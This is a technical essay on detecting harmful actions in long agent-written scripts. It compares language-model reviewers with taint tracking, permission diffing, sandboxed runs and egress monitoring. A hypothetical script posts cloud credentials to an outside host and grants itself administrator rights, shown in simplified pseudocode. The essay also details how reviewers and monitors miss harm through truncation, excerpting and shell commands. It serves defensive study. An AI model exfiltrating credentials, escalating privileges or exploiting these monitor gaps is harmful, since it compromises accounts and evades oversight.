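# Static analysis, sandboxed dry runs and egress monitoring alongside language-model code reviewers

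## Harmful actions in long scripts and the tools that look for them

Language models now write whole programs that run with access to real accounts, files and networks. A second language model often reads such a program first and decides whether it may run. Such a model, called a language-model reviewer, judges whether a script is harmful by reading the script or a record of its actions. Alongside the reviewer, an operator can use any of four computer security methods based on ideas that predate language models. Taint tracking follows sensitive data through the code. Permission diffing compares what the code could do with what its task requires. A sandboxed dry run executes the code in isolation and records its behaviour. Egress monitoring watches outgoing network traffic.

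Long scripts come from a change in how agents work. An agent is a language model that acts through tools, such as a command line or a web service. In the older pattern, the model calls one tool, reads the result and picks the next call. *Code execution with MCP*, a post by Anthropic, the developer of the Claude models, describes an alternative in which the model writes a program that calls the tools. In the post's example, this cuts the text the model has to process from 150,000 tokens (word fragments) to 2,000. The program passes data from one service to another, and the model receives only what the program prints or returns. Anthropic counts this as a gain for privacy, but it also means that no model checks the data as it moves. The post warns that such code needs a sandbox (an isolated environment that limits what running code can reach), resource limits and monitoring.

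Anthropic's *Introducing dynamic workflows in Claude Code* announces a feature of the company's coding agent in which Claude writes a script that directs tens to hundreds of subordinate agents in one session. According to Anthropic's documentation, the script holds the loops, branching and intermediate results, and a user at the command line can open the raw script before approving the run.

Many users will not open the script. Running a Python script of any length takes a single command, so one approval covers every line. Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2026), in *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight*, found that a sizable minority of users inside OpenAI had allowed every command beginning with "python", a rule under which nobody reads the script at all. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that 43% of active command-line users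 had rules that broad in June 2026.

Both companies have since put a language-model reviewer at this point. OpenAI's, called Auto-review, judges only actions that would cross the sandbox boundary, so a script that stays inside never reaches it. Anthropic's, called auto mode, sets aside the blanket rules. *How we built Claude Code auto mode* says the reviewer is instructed to judge what a script would do when it runs, regardless of how the launching command looks.

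### The example script

Take a Python script of 1,200 lines that a model has written for a company's operations team. Its task is to compress last month's web-server logs, upload them to a storage bucket (a named container for files at a cloud provider) and post a count to an internal metrics host. Nearly all of the 1,200 lines serve that task. Three places matter for a reviewer:

- Near line 240 the script reads a cloud credentials file. It needs the credentials for the upload.
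- Near line 910 it assembles a message labelled "diagnostics", includes the credentials in it, and sends it to a host outside the company.
- Near line 1,060 it attaches an administrator policy to its own service account, the account under which the script runs.

The read near line 240 is ordinary. AWS, Amazon's cloud-computing business, documents that its command-line tool keeps credentials in a plain-text file in the user's home directory, and that its programming libraries use the same file. Almost any script that uploads something to AWS will open that file, directly or through a library.

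AWS's version of the administrator policy permits every action on every service and resource in the account, which is far more than the upload needs, since it only writes to one bucket. AWS recommends least privilege, which means granting only the permissions a task requires. The call near line 1,060 can succeed only if the service account already has permission to change policies, and a log uploader has no reason to have that permission.

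The two harmful lines also make each other worse. In a cloud account, rights belong to the account, and the key only proves who is calling. Whoever received the credentials at line 910 therefore gains administrator rights when line 1,060 runs, and keeps them for as long as the stolen credentials stay valid.

### Exfiltration and privilege escalation

Line 910 is a case of exfiltration, which means sending data to a place where its owner did not want it to go. *Exfiltration* (2025), a glossary entry from the Open Source Security Foundation (OpenSSF), defines it, following the US standards institute NIST, as the "unauthorized transfer of information from a system". The upload to the storage bucket also moves data off the machine, and it is harmless only because the owner authorized it.

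Line 1,060 is a case of privilege escalation, which means gaining rights on a system beyond those that were granted. MITRE, a non-profit organisation that catalogues attack techniques, covers this step in its entry on cloud roles, *Account Manipulation* (2020). The entry describes someone with sufficient permissions attaching an additional policy to an account they control. It also lists groups that have done similar things in real intrusions, including LAPSUS$, which gave the global administrator role to accounts it had created inside its targets' cloud systems.

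A model-written script can expose data or take more access than its task needs, even when no adversary is involved. Anthropic's staff encountered both problems. In one session, an upload to an internal drive failed, and Claude tried to publish the same report on a public code-sharing site. In another, the task was to set up read-only access to billing data, and Claude chose a role with full administrative control. Anthropic reports that auto mode stopped both actions.

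Anthropic gives four reasons an agent might act harmfully. It may be overeager and use a credential it happened to find because that solves the user's problem. It may make an honest mistake about how much an action will affect. Instructions planted in a file or web page may hijack it, an attack known as prompt injection. Or the model may be misaligned and pursue a goal of its own, which Anthropic says it does not currently see in practice.

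Line 910 fits any of these. A model writing code to make failures easier to debug could add a helper that sends the script's whole configuration, including credentials, to an error-reporting service. That code might be identical to code written to steal the credentials, and they leave the company either way. This is a practical argument for tools that look at data and rights, because they can flag the line without establishing why it is there.

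### What the four tools observe

Static analysis examines a program without running it, while dynamic analysis runs the program and observes what it does. Guo, Liu and colleagues (2026) explain in *How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?* that dynamic analysis gives evidence of how code behaves rather than how it looks, but requires running untrusted code. Static analysis can also consider branches that a particular run would skip.

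The form of taint tracking that matters most here is static. It requires a list of sources, where sensitive data enters a program, and a list of sinks, where that data could do harm. The file read near line 240 is a source, and the network call near line 910 is a sink. The tool traces the path of data between them, across about 670 lines.

Permission diffing takes a script's effective capabilities, meaning everything the script could do with the calls it makes and the rights it holds, and subtracts the required capabilities, meaning what the stated task needs. In the example, this leaves the power to change account policies.

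A sandboxed dry run records the files a script opens, the programs it starts and the connections it attempts during one execution. The run takes place before the script is allowed to act for real.

An egress monitor observes the destinations, volumes and sometimes contents of network traffic leaving an environment. The message from line 910 goes to a host not mentioned in the task. The policy change at line 1,060 is harder for the monitor to detect because it is sent as a request to the same cloud provider that receives the logs.

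These tools address what happens when a model's decision reaches the operating system, which Rashidi (2026), in *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents*, distinguishes from the decision itself. Even a well-behaved model can do damage if nothing limits its actions, and the system can prevent harm by refusing a hijacked model's calls. Rashidi sorted 39 papers on execution security into 17 categories and found that papers rarely cite work in other categories. Network egress control and static analysis of agent-written code had one paper each. Much of what is known about these tools therefore comes from neighbouring fields, especially the detection of malicious packages in public code registries, where the code is usually shorter and usually written by a human attacker.

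### Capability and intent

Guo and colleagues tested 11 detectors on packages from npm, the public registry for JavaScript code. They trace most of the differences between detectors to the fact that harmless and harmful packages use the same calls. For example, a call that starts another program can run a build step or give an intruder remote control of the machine. Guo and colleagues use "capability" for what a call makes possible and "intent" for the purpose it serves, and they point out that a single call is not enough to determine intent.

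The calls in the example script reveal little on their own about whether it is harmful. *Bridging Expert Reasoning and LLM Detection* (2026), another work on malicious packages, defines a sensitive call as one that touches critical resources or performs privileged operations: reading files, using the network, starting processes, or running code generated on the fly. The script has to make such calls to do its job, since it must open the credentials file and use the network at least twice. A list of the sensitive calls in a harmless version of the script would look much like a list from the harmful version, apart from the policy change.

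Both works point out that a sequence of calls carries more information than a single call. Guo and colleagues give the example of a package that reads the machine's name, formats it as text and sends it out in a web request. They write that reading the name is ambiguous but the whole chain is unambiguous evidence of intent. That seems too strong, because an ordinary crash reporter does the same three things, and the example script might too when it posts its count to the metrics host. The cases differ in where the data goes and whether anyone asked for it to go there. Anthropic makes the same observation about publishing code, where the same command can be routine or an exfiltration depending on whether the code lands in the team's private repository or a public one.

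Evidence of intent therefore has to come from outside the calls, and for a model-written script the obvious source is the stated task. The reviewer in *Back to Basics* (2026), a work on monitoring coding agents, receives a description of the task and a list of the agent's actions. It is instructed to look for signs such as access to files that are clearly irrelevant to the task, or attempts to reach or transmit sensitive data "unnecessarily". By that test, line 240 passes and line 910 fails, even though both handle the same credentials.

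A stated purpose is also easy to fake. *Magnet* (2026), which concerns people who misuse language models across many sessions, describes a user who introduces a worrying question as research for a class project. It proposes judging capability and intent separately, so that one convincing story cannot disable the whole defence. In a script, a comment, a function name, or the label "diagnostics" on a message full of credentials can mislead a reviewer in the same way. For this reason, Anthropic shows its reviewer only the user's messages and the agent's actions, not the agent's own explanations. The reviewer still sees any comments and names inside the script, because they are part of the action.

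*Magnet* also argues that capability is far harder to disguise than intent, because it shows up in concrete outputs and effects. This is persuasive for effects but less so for source code, because obfuscation (rewriting code so that it behaves the same but is harder to analyse) can hide which call a line makes.

### How to count the errors

Three measures describe a detector's performance. Recall is the share of harmful items it flags. The false-positive rate is the share of harmless items it flags. Precision is the share of flagged items that are harmful. Some sources, including Anthropic, report the false-negative rate instead of recall. This is the share of harmful items the detector misses, or one minus recall.

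Two detectors in the npm study show the trade-off between flagging what code can do and requiring evidence of what it is meant to do. In its static mode, Packj flags any package that uses one of 56 listed calls. Guo and colleagues ran it on 6,420 malicious and 7,288 harmless packages. Its recall was 98.69%, but it also flagged 6,234 of the harmless packages, a false-positive rate of about 86%, and its precision was 50.41%. GENIE, which requires much stricter evidence, had 99.76% precision but only 46.14% recall. One of its rules fires only when at least three different pieces of system information flow to the same web destination. A similar rule would miss line 910, which sends only one kind of secret to one place.

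A detector's precision depends on how common harmful items are. Nearly half of the packages in that test were malicious. The share is surely far lower among scripts that a company's own agents write, since Trębacz and colleagues report that Auto-review approves about 99% of the actions it judges. Suppose one script in a thousand is harmful, and a detector has a recall of 90% and a false-positive rate of 1%. Out of 100,000 scripts, it flags 90 of the 100 harmful ones and 999 of the 99,900 harmless ones. Its precision is then about 8%, so roughly eleven of every twelve alarms are false. On a test set that was half harmful, the same detector would have a precision of about 99%.

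## What language-model reviewers miss in long scripts

A language-model reviewer can miss harmful code in a long script because part of the script never reaches the model, or because the model overlooks the harmful lines or gives them a low score. Also, some of the facts that decide whether a line is harmful are not in the script.

Most measurements of these failures again come from packages written by human attackers, which only partly resemble an agent's script with two harmful lines among a thousand useful ones. Several of the tested models are also older than today's best, and the newest, GPT-5.6 Luna and DeepSeek V4 Flash, are low-cost. The studies are therefore better evidence of how reviews fail than of how often a current reviewer would fail on an agent's script.

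### A reviewer that judges code alone

The npm study by Guo and colleagues ran its 11 detectors in 16 variants. The detectors include rule-based static tools, a sandbox, machine-learning classifiers and two pipelines built on language models. The malicious packages came from five academic collections and from security advisories. Three experts reviewed each package, and it stayed in the set only if at least two agreed that it did something malicious, which removed 1,367 packages. The harmless packages are popular ones, because malware in a widely used package tends to be found quickly.

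The experts judged each package at the places that two of the tested tools had flagged, which may favour those two tools. Testing on popular packages puts all the detectors at a disadvantage, because popular packages set off more false alarms than randomly chosen ones.

SocketAI is the pipeline in the study that asks a model to judge code without outside evidence. The model writes a report on the package, criticises it, and then writes a final report. SocketAI's code is not public, so Guo and colleagues rebuilt it from its published prompts and ran it on GPT-4.1 mini, a small OpenAI model. They note that the commercial service may do better.

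The rebuilt SocketAI had 98.21% precision and 44.41% recall. It raised about 50 false alarms on the 7,288 harmless packages but missed 3,569 of the 6,420 malicious ones. It took 146 seconds per package, with packages averaging 47 files and roughly 3,000 lines.

Evasion cannot explain most of those misses. About 80% of the malicious packages used no evasion technique, so even if SocketAI missed every package that did, more than 2,300 of the packages it missed made no attempt to hide. Guo and colleagues trace the low recall to three features of the pipeline:

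- It reads at most 20 files per package, so it skips harmful code that lies deep in the directory structure.
- Its second round tells the model to challenge its own finding that code is malicious, and the model then talks itself out of correct detections.
- The model gives cautious scores, and much real malware ends up below the threshold of 0.5.

In the challenge round, the model could easily decide that line 910 of the example script is harmless. Asked to doubt its first impression, it could reasonably answer that programs often send diagnostics to an outside service. None of the three causes shows that GPT-4.1 mini cannot recognise malware. IntelGuard, which runs on the same model but first retrieves known malware for comparison, had a recall 49 points higher.

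### Text that never reaches the model

The 20-file limit was a design choice, but models also have a fixed limit, the context window, which is the most text they can process at once. *CASHEWS* (Noirot Ferrand, Adei and colleagues, 2026) gives typical windows as 200,000 to 1,000,000 tokens, and the reviewer's instructions must also fit within the window. If a file is too large, the detector has to split it, cut it short or skip it.

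One study tested three models, each in two workflows, on 4,884 npm files published between January 2025 and July 2026, half of them malicious. The six combinations missed 7–12% of the malicious files overall. On the 512 files longer than 25,000 tokens, they could scan only 69–86% and missed 28–40% of the malicious ones. These figures count unscanned files as harmless, because a registry could not check so many by hand. Asked a single question, GPT-5.6 Luna missed 34.9% of the malicious long files and, based on the published totals, about 5% of the malicious shorter ones.

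Whole code repositories exceed the input limit more often. *MalTotal* (Zhao, Wang and colleagues, 2026) gave 250 malicious repositories to DeepSeek-V3, and a quarter did not fit. The evidence about a program can also be too long. *Preflight* (Jandali, Sheybani and colleagues, 2026) tried to have GPT-5.4 give verdicts on compromised Python packages from the results of static checks and sandbox runs. All five requests exceeded the limit, so the verdicts came from fixed rules instead.

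The example script is much smaller than this. At 40 characters a line, its 1,200 lines come to 48 KB, or roughly 12,000 tokens, which fits any of these windows. A reviewer could still receive only part of it, since operators set lower limits to save money. The script may also share the window with the record of a long session, as it can in Anthropic's auto mode.

The truncation rule then determines what a reviewer misses. In *LLM-Enhanced Hierarchical Heterogeneous Graph Representation Learning for Malicious Python Package Detection*, Gao, Chen and colleagues (2026) joined all of a package's Python files into one text and cut it at the model's limit. They prioritized setup.py and \_\_init\_\_.py, where attackers often put harmful code. A single script has no such obvious place to look. A reviewer that kept only the first half of the example script would see the ordinary read near line 240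 but neither of the harmful lines.

### Scripts read in pieces

Some reviewers receive only excerpts. *SkillGate* (2026) describes a checker for skill files, which extend what a coding agent can do. A pattern filter first looks for suspicious text. GPT-5.4-mini then receives up to 500 characters on either side of each match, limited to 20 excerpts and 8,000 characters in total. Verdicts were more accurate with a moderate allowance of excerpts than with a tighter one, so the surrounding code evidently helps.

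For the example script, 8,000 characters is about a sixth of the text, or around eight full-size excerpts. A filter would probably match both the file read near line 240 and the network call near line 910. Most of the 670 lines between them would be missing, including the assignments that carry the credentials from one to the other. The excerpts would show the script opening a file it needs and, separately, sending a diagnostics message. If earlier matches had used up the allowance, the excerpts would not include line 910 at all.

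Attackers can spread out attacks on packages in the same way. Gao and colleagues describe one in which an installation script loads several modules, a function in one of them collects information about the machine, and another function sends it out. Each part looks fairly ordinary on its own. In their tests, the model Qwen3-14b caught 82% of malicious packages with fewer than ten import statements (lines that load other code) and 37% of those with ten or more. Packages with many imports also tend to be larger, so this comparison doesn't isolate the effect of spreading out an attack.

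When a file was still too large after shortening, Noirot Ferrand and colleagues sent the model only the three most suspicious pieces, those with the most sensitive sources and sinks. The model could then scan nearly every file, and fewer malicious files got through overall, but it missed some because the harmful code was in the fourth-ranked piece.

### Harmful lines among many harmless ones

A model can also miss harmful code that it was given in full. Zhao and colleagues showed DeepSeek-V3 the same malicious samples as whole repositories, as only the files with sensitive calls, and as short excerpts of only the malicious logic. For JavaScript, the model missed 16.3% of the repositories that fit in its context window and 2.0% of the excerpts.

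Those percentages come from small counts, seven misses out of 43 compared with one out of 50. In each of the other four languages, the model missed at most one repository. The researchers cut the excerpts by hand, already knowing where the harm was. They used no harmless samples, so the test does not show whether short excerpts cause more false alarms.

Gao and colleagues provide a larger comparison. They grouped packages by the total size of their Python code and chose harmless packages to match the malicious ones in size. Two of their four language models did well on small packages:

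| Model and measure | Under 5 KB | 5 KB or more | 700 KB or more |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-14b, recall | 91.51% | 57.72% | 35.45% |
| Qwen3-14b, precision | 98.03% | 96.84% | 97.50% |
| DeepSeek-R1-70b, recall | 97.25% | 43.22% | 17.27% |
| DeepSeek-R1-70b, precision | 76.19% | 60.08% | 32.20% |

Qwen3-14b was nearly always right when it flagged a large package, but it flagged far fewer of them. DeepSeek-R1-70b got worse in both respects. Its figures imply that, among packages of 700 KB or more, it flagged about 36% of the harmless ones and only 17% of the malicious ones, which is worse than guessing.

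Gao and colleagues attribute the decline to truncation. That may not be the whole explanation, because a 5 KB package is only about 1,300 tokens, and packages near the lower end of the large group would have fit in full. So the figures mix packages the models saw whole with packages they saw in part. The 48 KB example script would belong to the large group.

Cloudflare (2026), which runs customers' scripts on its network, reported in April that models detected nearly all malicious scripts under 500 KB but only 12–18% of those over 3 MB.

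Length has some effect on reviewers' accuracy even when programs are very short. *An Evaluation of Large Language Models for Detection of Malicious Python Packages* (Ryan, Khalil and colleagues, 2026) asked 13 models to name the specific signs of malice in 370 packages with a median length of 36 lines. The average F1 score, which combines precision and recall, was 0.38 for packages of more than 34 lines and between 0.47 and 0.49 for shorter ones. The correlation with length was weak (−0.26), and longer packages also contain more signs to find. The models named data exfiltration in only 35% of the cases where it was present. A reviewer can evidently flag a script as suspicious without telling the operator what to fix.

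### Scores that are too cautious or too suspicious

SocketAI's errors were mostly wrong approvals. The models that Ryan and colleagues tested tended instead to flag harmless packages when asked only whether a package was malicious. Precision was below 50% in about half of the combinations of model, prompt and temperature (a setting for how random a model's output is), while recall was below 50% in only 1.6% of them.

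This part of the study used only 10 malicious files and 93 harmless ones. GPT-4.1, the one proprietary model, was almost perfect. The average F1 score was 0.23 when the prompt included worked examples, compared with 0.74 for a plain question. An operator who changes a reviewer's prompt should therefore expect to measure the reviewer's errors again.

Noirot Ferrand and colleagues also ran SocketAI's three-round workflow with newer models, on single files instead of whole packages. It missed about 10% of the malicious files, compared with 56% of the malicious packages in the npm study. The two tests differ in their models, data and file limit, so it is hard to tell which change mattered most.

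Results from Noirot Ferrand and colleagues give some support to the idea that models discard correct detections when they criticize their own answers. GPT-5.6 Luna missed 9.5% of malicious files with the three rounds and 7.3% with one direct question. DeepSeek V4 Flash missed slightly fewer with the three rounds, 10.6% compared with 11.5%. The researchers say the extra rounds made sense for GPT-3.5 and GPT-4, which raised many false alarms, but now mainly add cost.

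Long records can raise suspicion scores as well as lower them. In *Paranoid Monitors*, Yang, Muhamed and colleagues (2026) lengthened the records of agents working on a simulated bank-transfer task. Beyond 30,000 tokens, standard monitors gave harmless records higher suspicion scores than malicious ones. Lowering the alarm threshold can correct a reviewer that is reluctant to flag, but when the ranking is reversed, it adds more false alarms than detections.

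### Facts that are not in the script

In the study by Ryan and colleagues, many of the signs that models missed most often take outside knowledge to recognise. The models missed 97% of the package names that imitate a popular package by adding a word, and spotting these requires knowing which packages are popular. They also missed 84% of the cases in which code sent data to a suspicious domain, where it helps to know the domain's reputation.

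The text of the example script likewise does not prove who owns the host that receives the diagnostics message, or show whether the service account has the permission that the call near line 1,060 needs. A strict reviewer could still block that call as unrelated to the task.

A harder case is a script whose task is to attach a company-defined policy called "log-reader". The script contains only the policy's name, while the rights it grants are listed in the cloud account. If someone has added administrator rights to that policy, the script is dangerous even though its text hasn't changed.

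Xu (2026), in *The Oversight Gap*, gives a mathematical limit for such cases. Balanced accuracy is the average of two shares: the harmful cases that a reviewer blocks and the harmless cases that it approves. For any reviewer that sees a single record,

balanced accuracy ≤ ½ + ½ × TV

The total variation distance (TV) measures how much the texts from harmless cases differ from the texts from harmful ones. It is 0 if both kinds of case produce the same texts with the same frequency, and 1 if they have no texts in common.

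Any reviewer approves some set of texts. Its balanced accuracy is ½ plus half the difference between the probability that a harmless case produces a text in that set and the probability that a harmful case does. The total variation distance (TV) is the largest such difference over all possible sets, so no reviewer's balanced accuracy can exceed ½ + TV/2. In the log-reader case TV is 0, so no model that reads only the script can do better than chance. If TV were 0.2, the best possible reviewer would reach 60%.

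Xu tested nine models, from Llama-3.1-8B to GPT-4o and Claude Sonnet 4, on records in which an assistant might show one customer's data to another. When the leaked value looked like a correct one, the models performed at chance, as the limit requires. When the value was clearly the wrong type, such as a blood group given as a delivery address, a 20-line program caught every leak, but the models averaged only 60.9%. Telling the models what to check closed 61% of the remaining gap.

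Xu also gave six of the models the missing fact, the value stored for that customer. Their balanced accuracy was 68.2% with the stored value alone and 100% when they also had an explicit rule for comparing it with the value shown. By the same logic, a list of the service account's rights would help a script reviewer most if it came with an instruction to compare those rights with what the task needs.

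## Static taint tracking: following data from a secret to the network

In the example script, line 240 reads the credentials and line 910 sends them out. A handful of assignments scattered over the 670 lines between them link the two, so the script's text contains the whole connection, even though it may not show what rights the service account holds. Static taint tracking finds the connection by applying the same few rules to every statement, whether it is at the top of a long file or in the middle.

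### The algorithm

Tools differ in detail, but most go through these steps:

1. Parse the code into a syntax tree, which records, for example, that line 240 assigns the result of a function call to a variable.
2. Build a control-flow graph, which connects each statement to the statements that can run directly after it, and a data-dependence graph, which connects each statement that sets a variable to the statements that use the value.
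3. Attach a label to the result of every source.
4. Apply a propagation rule to each statement to work out which labels its result carries.
5. Summarise each function, so that a call to it can pass labels from the arguments to the result.
6. Repeat the propagation until no label changes.
7. Report every path along which a label reaches a sink.

Let T(x) be the set of labels on a variable x. The usual rules are short:

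| Statement | Rule |
|---|---|
| x = constant | T(x) = ∅ |
| x = source() | T(x) = {secret} |
| x = f(y, z) | T(x) = T(y) ∪ T(z) |
| d[key] = y | T(d) = T(d) ∪ T(y) |
| x = sanitiser(y) | T(x) = ∅ |
| sink(y) | report if T(y) ≠ ∅ |

Most labels spread through the rule for x = f(y, z), which treats addition, text formatting, compression and encoding alike. If an input contains a secret, the tool marks the output as possibly containing it too. Where two branches of a program meet again, the tool takes the union of the labels from both, because either branch might have run.

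Loops make the repetition necessary, because a statement near the end of a loop can put a secret into a variable that a statement near the start uses on the next iteration. SCS, a scanner for agent skills that Zhao, Wang and colleagues (2026) present in *From Instructions to Exploits*, handles this with a worklist. Whenever a variable's state changes, SCS goes back to the statements that use the variable, and it stops when a round changes nothing. Its labels have five levels of sensitivity, from public to secret, and a value built from several inputs takes the highest level among them. The analysis always stops eventually, because each round can only add labels or raise their level, and a program has a finite number of variables.

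With function summaries, a tool doesn't have to analyse the same function again at every call. If a library's code is missing or too large to analyse, someone has to write the summaries by hand. In SCS, the summary for parsing JSON text passes every label on to the result. In the summary for a web request, the address affects the labels on the reply, but the data sent does not. If SCS has no summary for a call, it gives the result the labels of all the inputs.

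Large programs contain many functions unrelated to any secret. *TaintP2X* (He, Wang and colleagues, 2026) avoids most of them by searching from both ends. The tool, built on the open-source analyser Pysa, follows labels forward from the sources and traces dependencies backward from the sinks. It then looks for complete paths only through functions found in both searches.

These rules follow data that a program copies or computes with. They ignore implicit flow, in which the branch a program takes reveals information about the data. However, *SAGA* (2026), an analyser for Python, has an option to report branches that depend on sensitive data.

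### From line 240 to line 910

A taint tracker can find only the flows that its lists of sources and sinks describe. One published rule that closely fits the example script belongs to GuardDog, an open-source package scanner that the monitoring company Datadog introduced in *Finding malicious PyPI packages through static code analysis* (2022). The rule's sources include the machine's name, reads of the AWS credentials file, and two environment variables that hold AWS keys. In the simplified version that Datadog printed, the sink is any call to requests, a Python library for web traffic.

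Suppose the example script handles the credentials like this:

| Line | Simplified statement | Result |
|---|---|---|
| 240 | creds = read(credentials_file) | creds carries the credential label |
| 262 | config["auth"] = creds | config carries it |
| 310 | client = connect(bucket, creds) | client carries it |
| 655 | client.upload(archive) | archive has no label |
| 902 | details = {"version": v, "config": config} | details carries the label |
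| 907 | body = to_json(details) | body carries it |
| 910 | post(outside_host, body) | the label reaches a sink |

The tool reports the path 240, 262, 902, 907, 910. Anyone who doubts the alarm can check five lines instead of 1,200.

Line 310 uses the same credentials to log in to the storage bucket. This must not raise an alarm, because every harmless version of the script logs in too. If logging in triggered the rule, every upload script in the company would raise an alarm, and the operators would soon disable the rule. But under the union rule, the client object carries the credential label, and its upload method sends data over the network.

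AWS's libraries sign each request with the secret key but don't transmit it, whereas at line 910 the credentials are the content of the message. A precise tool therefore treats a particular argument of a call as the sink, rather than the whole call. SCS reports a risk of exfiltration when sensitive data reaches the payload of a web request. A similar rule from NyxSec, which publishes a code scanner, covers the body, headers and JSON content of outgoing requests. A tool with such a rule checks the archive at line 655, finds only logs in it, and reports nothing.

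An operator could instead exempt trusted destinations, which NyxSec's scanner also allows. That would stop the false alarm too, but the scanner would then not flag the script if it put the credentials into the archive and uploaded them to a bucket that half the company can read.

However, sinks that cover only some of a network call's arguments can miss leaks. *Unveiling Malicious Logic* (Ryan, Ifti and colleagues, 2025) reproduces code from a malicious Python package that encodes all the environment variables and appends them to the web address it requests. This request has no body to inspect, so the address must also count as a sink.

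Source lists need the same upkeep. Datadog later extended GuardDog's Python rule to cover sensitive SQLite databases, where browsers store credentials, because malware in the wild was reading them. A more common gap with model-written scripts is that a cloud library opens the credentials file for the script, so the source list should also include library functions that return credentials.

Taint tracking set up to find stolen secrets does not flag the policy change near line 1,060, however dangerous that call is. The call sends the name of an administrator policy, which is a constant and carries no label.

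### Over-tainting, under-tainting and sanitisers

A taint tracker can over-taint, labelling data that does not contain the secret and raising false alarms, or under-taint, losing the label on data that does contain the secret and missing thefts. Many design choices reduce one error but increase the other.

In the example, if the tool keeps a single label for the whole config dictionary, it treats everything the script later takes out of the dictionary as suspect. Suppose the script also stores the name of its log directory there. The tool then applies the credential label to that name and to the logs the script reads from the directory, so it flags the harmless upload at line 655. A tool that keeps a separate label for each key avoids this false alarm, but it can lose track of labels when the program computes a key at run time.

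A sanitiser is a function whose output the tool treats as clean. For exfiltration, this could be a function that replaces a key with asterisks or reduces a sensitive file to a count of its lines. A wrong entry in the list of sanitisers can hide a leak. If a function called "redact" returns its input unchanged, but the tool treats it as a sanitiser because of its name, the tool removes the label and does not flag line 910.

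He and colleagues used a language model to check sanitisers. Their tool looks for a different kind of flow, from a model's output to a dangerous call such as a shell command or a database query. With a model identifying additional sources, static analysis produced 263 candidates across 4,772 open-source projects, of which 168 were false alarms. The full tool also has a model examine the functions on each path and check whether an outsider could control the prompt. This cut the false alarms to 36, but it also reduced the real findings from 95 to 78. The tool found 27 of 35 known vulnerabilities.

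### One flow or three

GuardDog's exfiltration rule requires one flow from one source to one sink, while the data-theft query in GENIE, the much stricter detector from the npm study, requires at least three. They differ because the tools have different purposes. In *GENIE*, Gobbi and Kinder (2024) aimed to find relatives of one reported piece of malware. They wrote their queries for CodeQL, an analyser that stores a program's syntax tree and graphs in a database.

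One of Gobbi and Kinder's sample packages collects the machine's name, the user's home directory and the user's account details, puts them in an object, converts the object to text and writes it to a web request. A query for this package needs an extra propagation rule that labels the whole object when a value is stored in it. Because this rule could cause false alarms across a registry of 1.8 million packages, they required flows from all three sources. They also had to tell theft apart from user tracking, on which npm had no clear policy. Their 12 queries found 125 previously unreported malicious packages, with no false alarms. Analysing a family of malware and writing its query took 30 to 45 minutes on average.

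In the comparison by Guo and colleagues, GuardDog had 96.99% precision and 89.92% recall, and took 2.55 seconds per package. GENIE as a whole had 99.76% precision and 46.14% recall. These figures imply about 180 false alarms for GuardDog on the 7,288 harmless packages, and about 7 for GENIE.

If the same error rates held for 100,000 scripts of which 100 are harmful, GuardDog would catch 90 of the harmful ones and raise about 2,450 false alarms, while GENIE would catch 46 and raise about 100. An operator who blocks scripts automatically might prefer GENIE because it raises fewer false alarms, but one who passes flagged scripts to a second reviewer can tolerate GuardDog's higher number.

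GuardDog's 89.92% recall is limited evidence about taint tracking, and it is not an estimate of how often a source-to-sink rule would catch line 910. OpenSSF's *GuardDog* lists the scanner's components as checks on package metadata, text patterns, and rules for Semgrep, an analyser that supports taint tracking. Guo and colleagues credit taint analysis for GuardDog's good balance, but they also report that two of its 22 rules account for over 90% of its detections. One looks for abuse of installation scripts and the other for suspicious web addresses. A script that an agent wrote for its own company has no installation hook, and the address at line 910 may not look suspicious, so both rules could miss it.

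GENIE's queries match particular families of malware, so its recall depends heavily on which attacks are common at the time. Recall ranged from 3.79% to 72.17% across the time periods in the study.

A single flow should be enough to raise an alarm when the data is a credential, such as a secret key sent to an unfamiliar host. A machine's name is weak evidence on its own, so it makes sense to require two more items before raising an alarm. A tool that records the source of each label can apply both thresholds in the same run.

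### Why collecting and sending together stand out

Many harmless programs read the machine's name or send data, but far fewer send the name they read. A rule that flags only programs that do so therefore ignores most harmless uses of either call.

Guo and colleagues similarly found that detectors, on average, had the highest detection rate for packages that both collected and sent data. The average rate was 40.0% for packages that only collected data, 72.2% for packages that only sent it and 85.4% for packages that did both. For SAP_DT, a decision tree trained on statistical features of packages, the rate rose from 3.2% to 79.3%.

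That evidence is weaker than it looks. Of the 4,207 packages that collected data, 4,144 also sent it, so the rates for collection alone rest on only 63 packages. SAP_DT does not trace data, so its improvement can't come from tracing a path between the two calls. It may improve because packages with both behaviours resemble the malware in its training set. The argument for requiring a connected path is sound, but these numbers do not isolate the effect of that requirement.

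### Where ordinary code breaks the path

Labels stop wherever the program hands its data to something the tool does not analyse. No attempt at concealment is necessary.

The most common case is a shell command. A script can pass a command to the operating system's shell, and that command can make the network connection. If the tool's sinks are all web-request functions, it finds no sink in such a script. Guo and colleagues found malware moving toward this method. The average malicious package made 12.52 sensitive calls in 2021 and 6.82 in 2023. By 2024–25, 12.6% of malicious packages used only one or two such calls, and about half of those only ran a single shell command. Ryan and colleagues labelled 370 malicious Python packages statement by statement and found 244 instances of shell commands and 114 of the script itself exfiltrating data.

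Agents also use the shell constantly for innocent purposes. The example script could upload through AWS's command-line tool, which reads the credentials file itself, so neither the source nor the sink would appear in the Python code. An operator can add command execution to the list of sinks. The taint tracker then catches a secret that the script inserts into a command's text, but it also flags every legitimate command that needs a password. It still misses a command that reads and sends the secret without the script's help, unless it parses the command as code too.

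A second programming language causes the same problem on a larger scale. A CodeQL database covers one language, except that HTML and JavaScript can share one. When Gobbi and Kinder collected packages that npm had removed, they set aside six whose harmful part was a shell script. They also analyse only a package's own code, so they miss behaviour that continues in another package.

SCS tracks data across languages by combining them in one dependence graph. It has rules for 191 Python functions, 91 JavaScript functions and 59 shell commands. It also covers a skill's written instructions, which a language model translates into simple statements such as "v0 = read_file(path)". Zhao and colleagues illustrate the need for this with a real skill for editing PowerPoint files. Its instructions tell the agent to run a "backup" script on the finished presentation, and the script sends the file to a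 fixed outside server. The instructions describe a routine backup and the script uploads whatever file it receives, so neither reveals on its own that the presentation is being leaked.

Averaged across five models, SCS had 95.2% recall and 80.2% precision on a set of 117 malicious and 117 harmless skills. These figures imply that it flagged nearly a quarter of the harmless skills. The models correctly translated more than 92% of instruction steps, so SCS will still lose track of some flows where a model mistranslates a sentence.

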